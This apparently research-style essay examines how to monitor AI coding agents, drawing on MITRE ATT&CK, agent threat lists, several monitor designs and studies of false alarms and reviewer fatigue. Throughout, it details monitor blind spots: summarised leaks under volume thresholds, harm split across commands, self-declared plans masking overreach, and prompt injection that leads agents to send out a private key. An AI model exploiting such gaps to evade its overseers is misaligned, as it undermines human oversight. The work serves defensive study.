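OpenAI's layers of monitoring suit one company watching its own models. A general scheme would list each threat with the content a monitor has to read for it. The closest existing example is MITRE ATT&CK, a public catalogue of techniques that attackers have used against computer systems. The American non-profit MITRE runs the catalogue and pairs nearly every technique with the records a defender needs to detect it.

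### From an attack to a log record

MITRE ATT&CK's *Detection of Data Destruction Across Platforms via Mass Overwrite and Deletion Patterns* (2025) gives the evidence for a technique called Data Destruction. For Linux, the chain from technique to evidence looks like this:

```
technique            Data Destruction
detection strategy   mass overwriting and deletion
analytic             many recursive deletions or overwrites on Linux
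data components      process creation     file deletion
log entries          execve               unlink, unlinkat, openat, write
```

An analytic describes suspicious behaviour on one platform, and a data component is a type of event. The log entries are system calls, such as `execve`, which starts a program, and `unlink`, which deletes a file.

MITRE released the current version of ATT&CK, version 20, in October 2026. MITRE ATT&CK's *Updates* (2026) counts 703 strategies for the 706 techniques and sub-techniques in that version's Enterprise part. The release adds Enterprise strategies but lists no changes to existing ones. It also revises some analytics and the definitions of several data components, including process creation.

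Command B from the earlier example leaves both kinds of evidence, because it starts `rm`, which then deletes the folder's files. Command A starts git and never starts `rm`. But the audit log can also record a program's arguments, and a rule that searched them for `rm -rf` would again flag A by mistake. The Linux analytic suggests filtering by the program's path, which avoids this error, but the Windows one suggests tuning on the command line's text. So the designer of a monitor has to choose which part of each record to inspect, as well as which log.

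Other analytics in the same strategy cover macOS, cloud services, virtual machine hosts and containers. For cloud services, the evidence is a request such as `DeleteBucket`, which removes a storage area. An agent with a cloud tool could make that request without a shell, so a monitor that reads only shell commands would miss it.

The strategy assumes an attacker who destroys a lot at once, and some of its analytics have thresholds for the number or speed of deletions. An agent's mistakes fit this pattern less well. Deleting a build folder with 10,000 replaceable files could cross a threshold, while deleting the only copy of a database might not, because it might be a single file. A record of that deletion would also come too late to prevent it.

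The MITRE ATT&CK technique closest to a leak is sending stolen data to a legitimate service such as Google Drive. MITRE ATT&CK's *Detection Strategy for Exfiltration Over Web Service* (2025) relies mostly on evidence surrounding the data: which process opened the connection, which files it read, which service it contacted and how much it sent. One analytic lists network content as a data component, but the log entry beside it records connections to cloud storage. Payload inspection appears instead in MITRE ATT&CK's *Exfiltration Over Web Service* (2020), which recommends data loss prevention as a mitigation.

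Data volume is a poor signal for an agent that summarises, because one sentence about the Brightwell plant would be far below any threshold. The technique's page records a campaign in which attackers had Claude Code summarise collected data before they sent it out. A network connection from a program that doesn't normally make one is also a weak signal for a coding agent, which may run new scripts all day.

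### What supports MITRE's pairings

*Context to Confidence* (Cunningham and Feffer, 2026) describes how a MITRE research centre looks for the smallest useful set of logs for an attack technique. The researchers start from the technique's data components, find real logs that record them, and check which of those logs public detection rules already use. A log belongs in the set if it helps separate malicious from harmless activity and is detailed, fast and robust enough to justify the cost of collecting it.

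The method is systematic, but it depends on expert scores and existing practice. Companies in the project validated the scoring, but the article includes no figures for how many attacks a defender would miss without a given log. The pairings are therefore informed advice about where to look.

Security teams can also overestimate how much a pairing covers. *Beyond the Heatmap* (Feffer, 2026) explains that teams often colour a technique green on a chart once they have a rule labelled with it. But there may be several ways to carry out the technique. For example, an attacker can create a scheduled task on Windows through PowerShell, the registry or a command-line program, and each route leaves different evidence. If a technique has eight known routes and a team's rules can detect two, Feffer reports the coverage as 2/8. *Putting Detection Coverage to the Test*, a case study of 144 public rules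 by the Center for Threat-Informed Defense, found that the labels alone don't show how deep or how good the coverage is.

Feffer also rates each signal on how hard it is to avoid and how well it separates malicious from harmless activity. These two qualities often conflict. A search for `rm -rf` is easy to avoid even by accident, since a script can delete files without those characters. Deletion system calls are much harder to avoid, but ordinary builds make them constantly.

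*Ambiguous Techniques* (Feffer, Cunningham and Sundar, 2025) calls a technique ambiguous when its observable traces don't reveal the intent, as when someone looks up a machine's network settings. The paper looks to context to resolve these cases. For an agent, the most useful context is often the user's request, but neither of the two strategies above includes it. ATT&CK describes intruders, who don't act for a user, so it offers little help with overeager actions.

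### Threat lists for AI systems

MITRE also maintains ATLAS, a catalogue of attacks on AI systems. *MITRE ATLAS Grows through Collaboration with CTID and Industry* (Cunningham and Dotter, 2026) describes it as a knowledge base of tactics, techniques and mitigations. Mitigations are changes a defender should make, and they may not determine what a monitor should read.

OWASP, a foundation that publishes software security guidance, lists ten risks for agents: goal hijacking, tool misuse, abuse of identity and privilege, supply chain weaknesses, unexpected code execution, poisoned memory, insecure messages between agents, cascading failures, exploitation of human trust, and rogue agents.

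OWASP's list mixes causes with effects, so an incident can belong to several categories. *Cross-Layer Semantic Flow Reconstruction for Attack Detection in Agentic Systems* builds ten attack scenarios from the list, and nine have two or more of its labels. The tenth is labelled only as unexpected code execution, and in it a malicious web page leads a group of agents to write a script, read a private login key and send the key to an outside address. A monitor might catch this attack by inspecting the web page, the script, the file access or the upload, but the label doesn't indicate which to inspect.

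In *Intrusion Detection for Agentic Processes*, Brömme (2026) considers ATLAS and the OWASP list useful for deciding which threats to cover, but notes that they don't by themselves define what counts as evidence while an agent is running. That seems fair, since a team could use either list to check for missing threats but would still have to work out what content to inspect for each.

### Separate scanners or one reader

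Some working systems do make that choice. Meta released *LlamaFirewall* (2025) as an open-source set of safeguards for agents. The Hacker News (2025) describes three scanners, each with its own material:

| Scanner | What it inspects | What it looks for |
|---|---|---|
| PromptGuard 2 | incoming text | attempts to override the model's rules or inject instructions |
| AlignmentCheck | the agent's reasoning | signs that an attacker has changed the agent's goal |
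| CodeShield | code the agent writes | insecure or dangerous code |

Each check inspects the content where its problem becomes visible. An injected instruction appears in incoming text, but the agent may ignore it, so AlignmentCheck checks whether it affected the agent. CodeShield uses static analysis, which examines code without running it. Some of the harm it looks for falls outside the five threat classes used so far, because a security hole may hurt nobody until someone exploits it months later.

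AScope, the system in *Cross-Layer Semantic Flow Reconstruction*, instead gives one model three policies. It first joins the agent's log to operating system events, extracts sensitive items such as passwords, and ranks the resulting chains of events by risk. The model then reads the top-ranked chains and applies all three policies to them:

| Policy | Evidence it uses | Violation |
|---|---|---|
| Intent | the user's request and the agent's declared plan, compared with its actions | an action outside the permitted goals or resources |
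| Data flow | sensitive items and the destinations in the chain | a sensitive item goes to an untrusted destination |
| Privilege | a model's estimate of how much privilege each party has | a party gains control of something more privileged without permission |

Each policy has a weakness that comes from its evidence or from the steps before it. The agent's plan helps define what is permitted, so an overeager agent could plan an unauthorised deletion and then appear to stay within bounds. The data-flow policy reduces each web address to its domain, so it shares the blind spot of a sandbox's domain list. The ranking multiplies an event's risk by the sensitivity of the listed items in it, so an event with no listed items scores zero. The list includes some dangerous commands, but a harmful action that isn't on it may never reach the model.

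The researchers removed parts of AScope in turn, using the ten scenarios. They scored each version with F1, which is high only if a detector catches most of the harmful events and most of its alarms are right:

| Version | F1 |
|---|---|
| Complete | 85.3% |
| Without the stage that analyses chains of events | 78.3% |
| Without the extraction of sensitive items | 62.0% |
| Without joining events into chains | 21.9% |

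The policies were never removed one at a time, so the test doesn't show whether each one helps. Removing the whole analysis stage, where the model applies the policies, lowered performance by only seven points, so the effects of individual policies would be hard to measure.

The last row is more informative. Without the chains, the same model applied the same policies to the raw log of about 2,000 entries per scenario and did very badly. This counts against giving a model everything, but it doesn't favour separate readers, because the successful version also used one model for every threat.

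The researchers also compared AScope with AlignmentCheck on 645 recorded sessions from AgentDojo, the benchmark that Costa and colleagues used for FIDES. Both detectors received the same evidence and used GPT-5.6 Sol. Each caught 284 of 288 successful attacks. Of the other 357 sessions, AlignmentCheck wrongly flagged 9.8% and AScope 22.7%.

AScope's extra questions therefore caught no additional attacks in this test and came with more false alarms, though some of those alarms involved real attacks that had failed. AgentDojo also has no operating system events, the evidence AScope was designed to add.

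### Keeping process records apart from content

Brömme instead proposes a detector that judges the steps an agent takes, mostly without interpreting the text it handles. Each observation records the type of event, who acted, what they acted on, when it happened and which source reported it. The detector compares these records with a list of expected events, such as an approval before each deployment.

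Brömme describes seven kinds of deviation:

- a required event is missing from the records
- events happen in the wrong order
- an agent contacts a tool, agent or data source it isn't allowed to use
- an agent keeps trying to reach something after a refusal
- two sources give conflicting records
- the monitoring itself has gaps or signs of a bypass
- an action follows contact with untrusted content, with a traceable path between them

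Most of these don't require reading documents or messages, so hostile text has little opportunity to influence the result. When content does need interpreting, Brömme uses an isolated analyser, which may be a language model. The detector receives the analyser's output as a claim with limited weight. The analyser can't change the rules, credentials or stored findings.

This separation exists because an agent can follow every rule and still produce a document with instructions aimed at the monitor. A one-way connection between agent and monitor doesn't solve the problem, because the hostile text travels in the permitted direction. Isolation doesn't remove the risk either, because a manipulated claim can still affect a finding if the rules let the analyser's claims do so.

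The design also records what the monitor could see. Suppose an agent deploys a program and the detector finds no record of the required approval. The detector marks the approval as "unobserved" if the approval log was working throughout, or "unknown" if the log was down for part of that time. Even "unobserved" doesn't prove that nobody approved, since a manager may have agreed by phone.

Process records are weakest when every step is legitimate and the harm is in the content. If an agent got approval to email a supplier, used the correct tool and wrote to the correct address, but mentioned the Leeds closure, the records would all look normal. Brömme's scheme also has no implementation or tests, so its pairings rest on argument alone.

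### Does it help to know what the agent is for?

The same request can be harmless for one agent and wrong for another. *Intent-Aware Protection for AI Agents* (Copty, Haiby and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of analysing a prompt injection, which is ordinary work for a security agent. A travel agent has no reason to act on such text.

Copty and colleagues at Microsoft describe each agent's purpose in an intent profile. A model extracts the profile from the organisation's policies, the agent's role and the developer's configuration. If these conflict, the organisation's policies come first and the configuration last. The profile lists the agent's mission, permitted tasks, limits on tools and data, and prohibited behaviour. User requests do not affect it.

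They tested the profile on 887 synthetic interactions with 35 agents. A classifier had to sort each one as benign, innocently out of scope, a deliberate misuse of the agent, or an attack:

| What the classifier read | Average F1 over the four classes | F1 for out-of-scope requests |
|---|---|---|
| The interaction | 43% | 2% |
| The interaction and the original policies, role and configuration | 45% | 8% |
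| The interaction and the profile | 79% | 76% |

The middle row is surprising. The original documents raised the average by only two points while the profile raised it by 36, even though the profile is a summary of those documents and can't contain more information about the agent's purpose than they do. The classifier had the necessary evidence in both cases but used it much better when it was organised. Matching content to a threat may therefore involve preparing the content as well as selecting it.

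The size of the gain may not carry over to real agents. The researchers used a model called MAI-Thinking-1 to screen the synthetic interactions and dropped those whose labels it didn't support. They say it also extracted the profiles, so the remaining interactions may suit its way of describing an agent's limits. However, a manual check of 100 interactions found 98 of the labels correct.

A second test used over 10,000 AgentDojo sessions, in which the state of the simulated accounts showed whether an attack had succeeded. The researchers measured AUROC, the probability that a monitor gives a randomly chosen successful attack a higher risk score than another randomly chosen session:

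| Monitor | AUROC |
|---|---|
| Session only | 84.3% |
| Session and the agent's configuration | 89.7% |
| Session and the profile | 94.9% |
| AlignmentCheck | 90.9% |

Knowing more about the agent also helped on this benchmark, which came from different researchers. But the profiles also covered how far to trust tool results and where the arguments of a tool call may come from, so some of the improvement may come from that security advice rather than from the description of the agent's purpose.

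The best monitor also depends on how a team uses the scores. At the fixed threshold in the study, the profile monitor caught 93.3% of successful attacks and AlignmentCheck caught 91.2%. About 24% of the profile monitor's alarms were false, compared with 4% for AlignmentCheck. A different threshold could reduce the profile monitor's false alarms. Most of the sessions without a successful attack contained a failed one, and only 97 had no attack, so the test provides little evidence about false alarms in ordinary work.

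AlignmentCheck compares an agent's actions with the user's request, whereas the profile monitor compares them with the agent's purpose. The profile is the better reference when the user is misusing the agent. It probably helps less with a general coding agent, whose purpose covers deleting files, running scripts and uploading code. A useful profile for such an agent would need limits specific to the project.

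### Threats and content for a coding agent

The table below applies the evidence so far to a coding agent. "E" marks entries supported by at least one experiment, and "A" marks those supported only by argument. Some of the experiments used office or messaging agents, so their results may be weaker evidence for coding agents. Two entries are recommendations to hide material only from a monitor that can approve actions, because another monitor may need to read it.

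| Threat | Content needed | Content better withheld | Suitable mechanism | Remaining blind spot |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Destructive commands | programs, options and paths (E); current state of the files (A) | quoted text that nothing will run (A) | rules that know what programs do (E), inside a sandbox (A) | harm spread over several commands (E) |
| Data leaks | payload and destination (E); who can read the destination (A) | the requester's explanation (A) | comparison with protected records (E); labels for reworded data (E) | secrets that nobody registered (E) |
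| Prompt injection | labels showing whether untrusted text reached the agent (E); tool results, for warnings (A) | tool results, from a monitor that can approve actions (A) | label checks before actions with consequences (E) | false facts in a file the user told the agent to trust (E) |
| Overeager actions | user messages and tool calls (E) | the agent's explanations and tool results (E) | a separate reviewer model (E) | misjudged consent (E) |
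| Concealed intent | reasoning as well as actions (E) | reasoning, from a monitor that can approve actions (A) | a second monitor that can only object (A) | aims the model doesn't write down (E) |

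## What goes wrong when one rule is applied to every risk?

Instead of treating each row of that table separately, a team could run one monitor with one threshold for every kind of harm. This would be simpler to build, and people would have only one kind of alarm to learn. The first problem is that agents rarely do anything harmful.

### Most alarms are false when harm is rare

Suppose a medical test is right for 99% of sick people and 99% of healthy people, and one person in 10,000 has the disease. Someone who tests positive has only about a 1% chance of being ill, because the healthy people who test positive far outnumber the sick. Axelsson (2000), in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, applied this arithmetic to systems that search computer records for signs of a break-in.

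Axelsson imagined a small office network that produces a million records a day, 20 of them from break-ins. If a detector caught all 20 and raised a false alarm on just one harmless record in 100,000, a third of its alarms would still be false. If it caught only 70% of the break-in records, 42% of its alarms would be false, which isn't much worse. The false positive rate therefore limits such a system more than its detection rate does.

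The error rates that Anthropic published for auto mode's reviewer show the same effect. Assume that 10 in every 10,000 actions are harmful, and use the miss rates for real overeager actions:

```
fast stage    harmless actions blocked    9,990 x 8.5%         =  849
              harmful actions blocked     10 x (1 - 6.6%)      =  9.3
              share of blocks correct     9.3 / (9.3 + 849)    =  1.1%

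both stages   harmless actions blocked    9,990 x 0.4%         =  40
              harmful actions blocked     10 x (1 - 17%)       =  8.3
              share of blocks correct     8.3 / (8.3 + 40)     =  17%
```

The second stage removes about 809 false alarms and lets through about one more harmful action. Even so, five blocks in six are wrong.

The share of correct blocks depends heavily on the assumption that ten actions in 10,000 are harmful. With the same error rates for both stages, about 2% of blocks would be correct if one action in 10,000 were harmful, and 68% if 100 were. Suppose leaks occur at the lower rate and overeager actions at the higher one. A single overall figure would then hide that most blocks for overeager actions are correct while almost all blocks for leaks are wrong, even though the monitor is equally accurate on both.

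Axelsson's calculation has this weakness because it treats every intrusion as the same kind of event. Axelsson acknowledges that a real system makes a separate yes-or-no decision for each type of intrusion, that some types are harder to detect, and that each may need a different amount of data.

A wrong block is less disruptive when the agent handles it instead of a person. In Claude Code's auto mode, the agent usually has to retry only once. But retries add up in long sessions. At a false positive rate of 0.4%, 5,000 harmless actions would produce 20 wrong blocks on average, the number at which Claude Code stops and turns to the user.

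In *Outside the Closed World*, Sommer and Paxson (2010) asked why companies rarely used machine learning to find unusual network traffic, despite years of research on it. One reason they gave was that each false alarm about an intrusion takes up an analyst's time, whereas a shop that recommends the wrong book loses little. Another was that unusual events aren't necessarily harmful, so the analyst still has to work out what each alarm means. They advised designers to start from a specific threat and keep the detector's scope narrow.

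For an agent, an alarm such as "this command sends a customer file to a public site" is more useful than "this session looks unusual" because it identifies the possible harm. The objection to alarms about unusual behavior is weaker when the monitor is a language model, which can explain its alarm in words and compare the action with the user's request, but false alarms are still a problem.

### What constant prompts do to people

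Axelsson had no experiments to draw on about how security staff respond to false alarms, but studies of power stations and factories suggested that most operators would have stopped trusting a device by the time half its alarms were false.

Anthropic reported in August 2026 that users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts. Most of those prompts are probably for safe commands, so the figure alone doesn't show that users are careless. Anthropic tested attention directly in a study of 1,053 paid testers, each of whom got one dangerous request. The testers knew they were in a study but not what it measured.

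| | Dangerous commands stopped |
|---|---|
| Testers, overall | 13.6% |
| Testers, early in a session | about 17% |
| Testers, after 50 or more prompts | about 5% |
| Auto mode, on the same commands | 89% |

Auto mode blocked 800 commands that a tester had approved, and testers refused only 6 that auto mode allowed. But Anthropic ran this comparison on its own product and used it to justify making auto mode the default. The testers also had less to lose than developers working on their own code. The decline over a session is more informative than the overall gap because it compares testers with testers rather than with auto mode.

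Too many prompts also lead users to turn them off. A quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start with permission checks disabled. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) studied 290 reports about agents and files. Of these, 80 involved actions that the user had set the agent to approve automatically, and another 31 involved prompts that gave the user too little information. For example, a prompt for `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it runs whatever code the script contains. A person who approves actions is acting as a monitor, so they also need the right evidence.

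People do much better with few prompts and plain wording. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had 113 people with no software background supervise a simulated day of 18 actions. Seven of the actions, such as reading private messages, went beyond what the user had asked for. People who had to decide on all 18 blocked 59.6% of these seven actions.

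In another version, a model approved eight harmless actions by itself and passed the other ten to the user, including all seven that went too far. Most prompts were then real warnings, but people blocked only 53.9% of the overreach. So removing false alarms didn't make people more careful, at least over a session this short. Many of the actions were also tempting, such as buying a $12 travel insurance policy, so people may have approved them because they liked the idea.

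Developers vary their attention only a little by type of action. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) reports a survey of 203 developers, 64% of whom said they often approve at least one type of action without close review. The share was only slightly lower, at 61%, among those who carefully review the agent's code. 21% said they often approve reading secrets and other sensitive files without close review, and 36% said the same of using the internet or outside services. These figures are self-reported.

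When a reviewer's attention is limited, asking them to approve every action can be less safe than asking about only some. In *Oversight Has a Capacity*, Turan (2026) simulated a reviewer who is perfectly reliable for a set number of requests and then gets worse with each further one. With a capacity of 25 requests, the safest policy sent 64% of 125 actions to the reviewer and let through 42% of the dangerous actions, while sending every action let through 57%. This pattern follows from the assumed fatigue, and the actions were deliberately hard, so the percentages don't predict real error rates. However, the fall from 17% to 5% in Anthropic's study suggests the assumption is reasonable.

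Attackers can also exploit reviewers' fatigue. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) describes work at Google DeepMind that anticipates attacks designed to wear reviewers down.

### "Is it malicious?" and "is it permitted here?"

A shared verdict causes a different problem, as the skill registry ClawHub shows. *ClawHub Security Signals* (Koc, Rivera and colleagues, 2026) compared three scanners on 67,453 skills. VirusTotal runs antivirus engines over a skill's files, a static analyser looks for dangerous patterns in its code and text, and SkillSpector uses a language model to help judge what its instructions would let an agent do.

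No two scanners overlapped on more than 10.4% of the skills that either flagged. A rule that rejects any skill flagged by at least one of the three scanners would remove 52.8% of the registry, while a rule that requires all three to agree would remove only 0.69%.

The 10.4% overlap makes the scanners look more different than they are. SkillSpector flagged 79% of the skills that the static analyser flagged. Even if it had flagged all of them, the overlap would have been only 13.5%, because SkillSpector flagged nearly half of all skills and the static analyser flagged under 7%.

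The registry's final verdicts are better evidence that the scanners specialise. A language model reaches each verdict after seeing the scanners' results and other information, such as where the skill came from. These are the shares of skills that each scanner flagged:

| Final verdict | Skills | VirusTotal | Static analysis | SkillSpector | At least one |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Clean | 41,743 | 4.4% | 3.2% | 32.7% | 36.6% |
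| Suspicious | 25,504 | 12.7% | 12.0% | 75.3% | 79.1% |
| Malicious | 206 | 72.8% | 12.6% | 6.8% | 75.7% |

Adding the other two scanners to VirusTotal raises the share of malicious skills caught from 72.8% to 75.7%, but it also raises the share of clean skills flagged from 4.4% to 36.6%. VirusTotal alone would miss most suspicious skills, which may ask for too much access or hide what they do. Whether a scanner is worth its false alarms therefore depends on what the registry wants to find. The verdicts come from a model that saw the scans, so they can't show which scanner was right. Of the 206 skills the model judged malicious, 50 had no scanner flag.

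None of these scanners checks skills against what a particular user allows. Of the 29,257 skills that passed every check in the registry, Taneja and Weber found 705 that tell the agent to do something many operators forbid, nearly always downloading code from the internet and running it. They audited 100 of these and found no sign of malicious intent in any that had been correctly flagged.

The number 705 overstates how common the practice is, because 506 of the skills come from one publisher that repeats the same installation command. Altogether, 135 publishers gave such instructions. Taneja and Weber based the phrase "many operators forbid" on two published security standards and did not survey operators.

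Their distinction holds whatever the exact count. Suppose a two-person startup lets its agent run a well-known company's installer, and a bank forbids its agents to run any downloaded script. The skill is identical in both places, so a registry gives both the same verdict. "Clean" is wrong as permission for the bank, and "blocked" is wrong for the startup:

```
is it malicious?         depends on   the skill
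is it permitted here?    depends on   the action, the machine and the operator's policy
```

A better scanner can't fix this, because the facts that distinguish the startup from the bank don't exist when the registry scans the skill. A monitor on the user's machine can access those facts. But a monitor that inspects only the installation command may miss the publisher's history of distributing malware, which the registry could have on record.

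The two answers can work together if neither replaces the other. Taneja and Weber suggest that when a registry marks a skill as suspicious, the monitor could require approval for every action the skill leads to, but they haven't tested this.

### Specialised monitors add up their false alarms

Splitting one monitor into several has a price. If any monitor can block an action, a harmless action has to get past all of them. With five independent monitors that each wrongly block 1% of harmless actions:

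```
share of harmless actions blocked  =  1 - 0.99^5  =  4.9%
```

Out of 9,990 harmless actions, the five monitors would block about 490, compared with about 100 for a single monitor that wrongly blocks 1% of them. Even if the five caught all ten harmful actions, only 2% of their blocks would be correct. They would block fewer harmless actions if they made the same mistakes, but that is less likely when they read different material.

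For the five monitors together to match the 0.4% false-alarm rate of auto mode's reviewer alone, each would have to stay at about 0.08%. To be 95% confident that one monitor's rate was below 0.08%, a team would need to see it review about 3,700 harmless actions without a false alarm.

The monitors wrongly block fewer harmless actions in total if each checks only the actions that could cause its kind of harm. A leak monitor can skip a command that sends and shares nothing, and a deletion monitor can skip a web search. If each of the five monitors checked a different fifth of the actions, together they would wrongly block 1% of harmless actions. The actions must then be sorted correctly, because an action sent to the wrong monitor gets no useful check.

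Specialised monitors also leave gaps between them. For example, a command that copies private records into a public web folder would get past both a deletion monitor and an upload monitor. Taneja and Weber describe two more cases their own system can't detect. In one, a skill automates an account while avoiding detection, using tool calls that each look ordinary. In the other, an agent gets far more access to private data than its job needs, but no single action is out of proportion.

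A general reviewer that reads the user's request and the agent's actions might catch some of these. It would work best with a high threshold, because the specialists already cover the common harms and its false alarms add to theirs. Axelsson's list of open problems includes making sure that several security measures together are at least as good as each one alone. Adding a monitor can't reduce what the group blocks, but if the combined alarms lead people to switch the monitors off, the combination is worse than any one of them.

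### Separate thresholds and error budgets

A monitor that estimates the chance of harm should block when the expected cost of allowing the action is higher than the expected cost of blocking it:

```
block if   chance of harm x cost of a miss  >  chance of no harm x cost of a false alarm
```

Turan assumes that missing a moderate risk is 5 times as bad as a false alarm, and missing a severe one is 50 times as bad. By the rule above, a monitor should block moderate risks when the chance of harm is above 17% and severe ones when it is above 2%. An action with a 10% chance of harm should then go ahead if the harm would be moderate but not if it would be severe. A single threshold would treat both cases the same way and get one of them wrong. The calculation needs accurate probabilities, which a language model may not give, and people may disagree about how bad each mistake is.

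The same reasoning applies to auto mode's second stage, which removes 809 false alarms when ten of 10,000 actions are harmful. It also misses about 1.04 more of the harmful actions if they are overeager, or 0.39 more if they resemble the synthetic leaks. The second stage is therefore worth having if a missed overeager action does less harm than about 780 false alarms, or a missed leak does less harm than about 2,100.

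When a false alarm causes one retry, a team might keep the second stage for deletions in a test project and skip it for possible leaks of customer data. Anthropic's figures don't show how many of the fast stage's false alarms concerned leaks. If only a few did, skipping the second stage for leaks would cause far fewer than 809 extra retries.

To set an error budget, a team decides how many errors people can tolerate in total and divides that number among the monitors. A team that accepts 40 wrong blocks in 10,000 actions might allow 25 from the monitor for leaks, 5 from the monitor for deletions inside a project with good backups, and 10 from all the others. Blocks that a person has to handle need a much smaller budget than blocks the agent can handle by itself.

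Misses need a budget as well, especially when a monitor stops asking about actions that have gone well in the past. Taneja and Weber work out how many clean approvals in a row should come first. If the true failure rate is e, the chance of N clean runs is (1 - e)^N, and N has to be large enough to bring that chance down to 5%:

| Highest failure rate the operator accepts | Clean approvals needed |
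|---|---|
| 10%, for example for documentation | 29 |
| 5%, for example for ordinary shell commands | 59 |
| 2%, for example for business logic | 149 |

Ten clean approvals can't rule out a failure rate of 25.9%, yet the source paper's own product uses that same threshold for every class that can earn an exemption. The calculation is also optimistic, because a person reviewed every counted run and may have stopped the bad ones. That makes the record weaker evidence of how the agent behaves alone.

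Limiting the failure rate of each action doesn't limit the total number of failures. At a failure rate of 0.5%, 1,000 unattended actions produce five failures on average, and there is a 99.3% chance of at least one. An operator who can accept only one failure a year has to work backwards from that number to a limit for each action. The same problem arises across categories. If 100 combinations of action and resource each had a failure rate exactly at the limit, about five would qualify for an exemption by luck.

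Someone also has to choose the separate rules, and users may not be the right people to do it. Wu and colleagues recommend different approval rules for different types of action. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) suggests that prompts should show whether an action can be undone, because two actions of the same type can carry different risks. In one version of Yan's experiment, participants chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories: spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting things and reading private data.

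These participants blocked only about 40% of the overreach, compared with 59.6% for those who decided on every action. They had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, so the separate rules worked much like a single rule. They then approved two thirds of the overreach actions they were asked about. Yan added participants to this group after random assignment had ended, so the groups may have differed in other ways. The experiment tested rules that users write, so it isn't evidence against thresholds set by a monitor's designers, such as auto mode's ban on sending secrets out.
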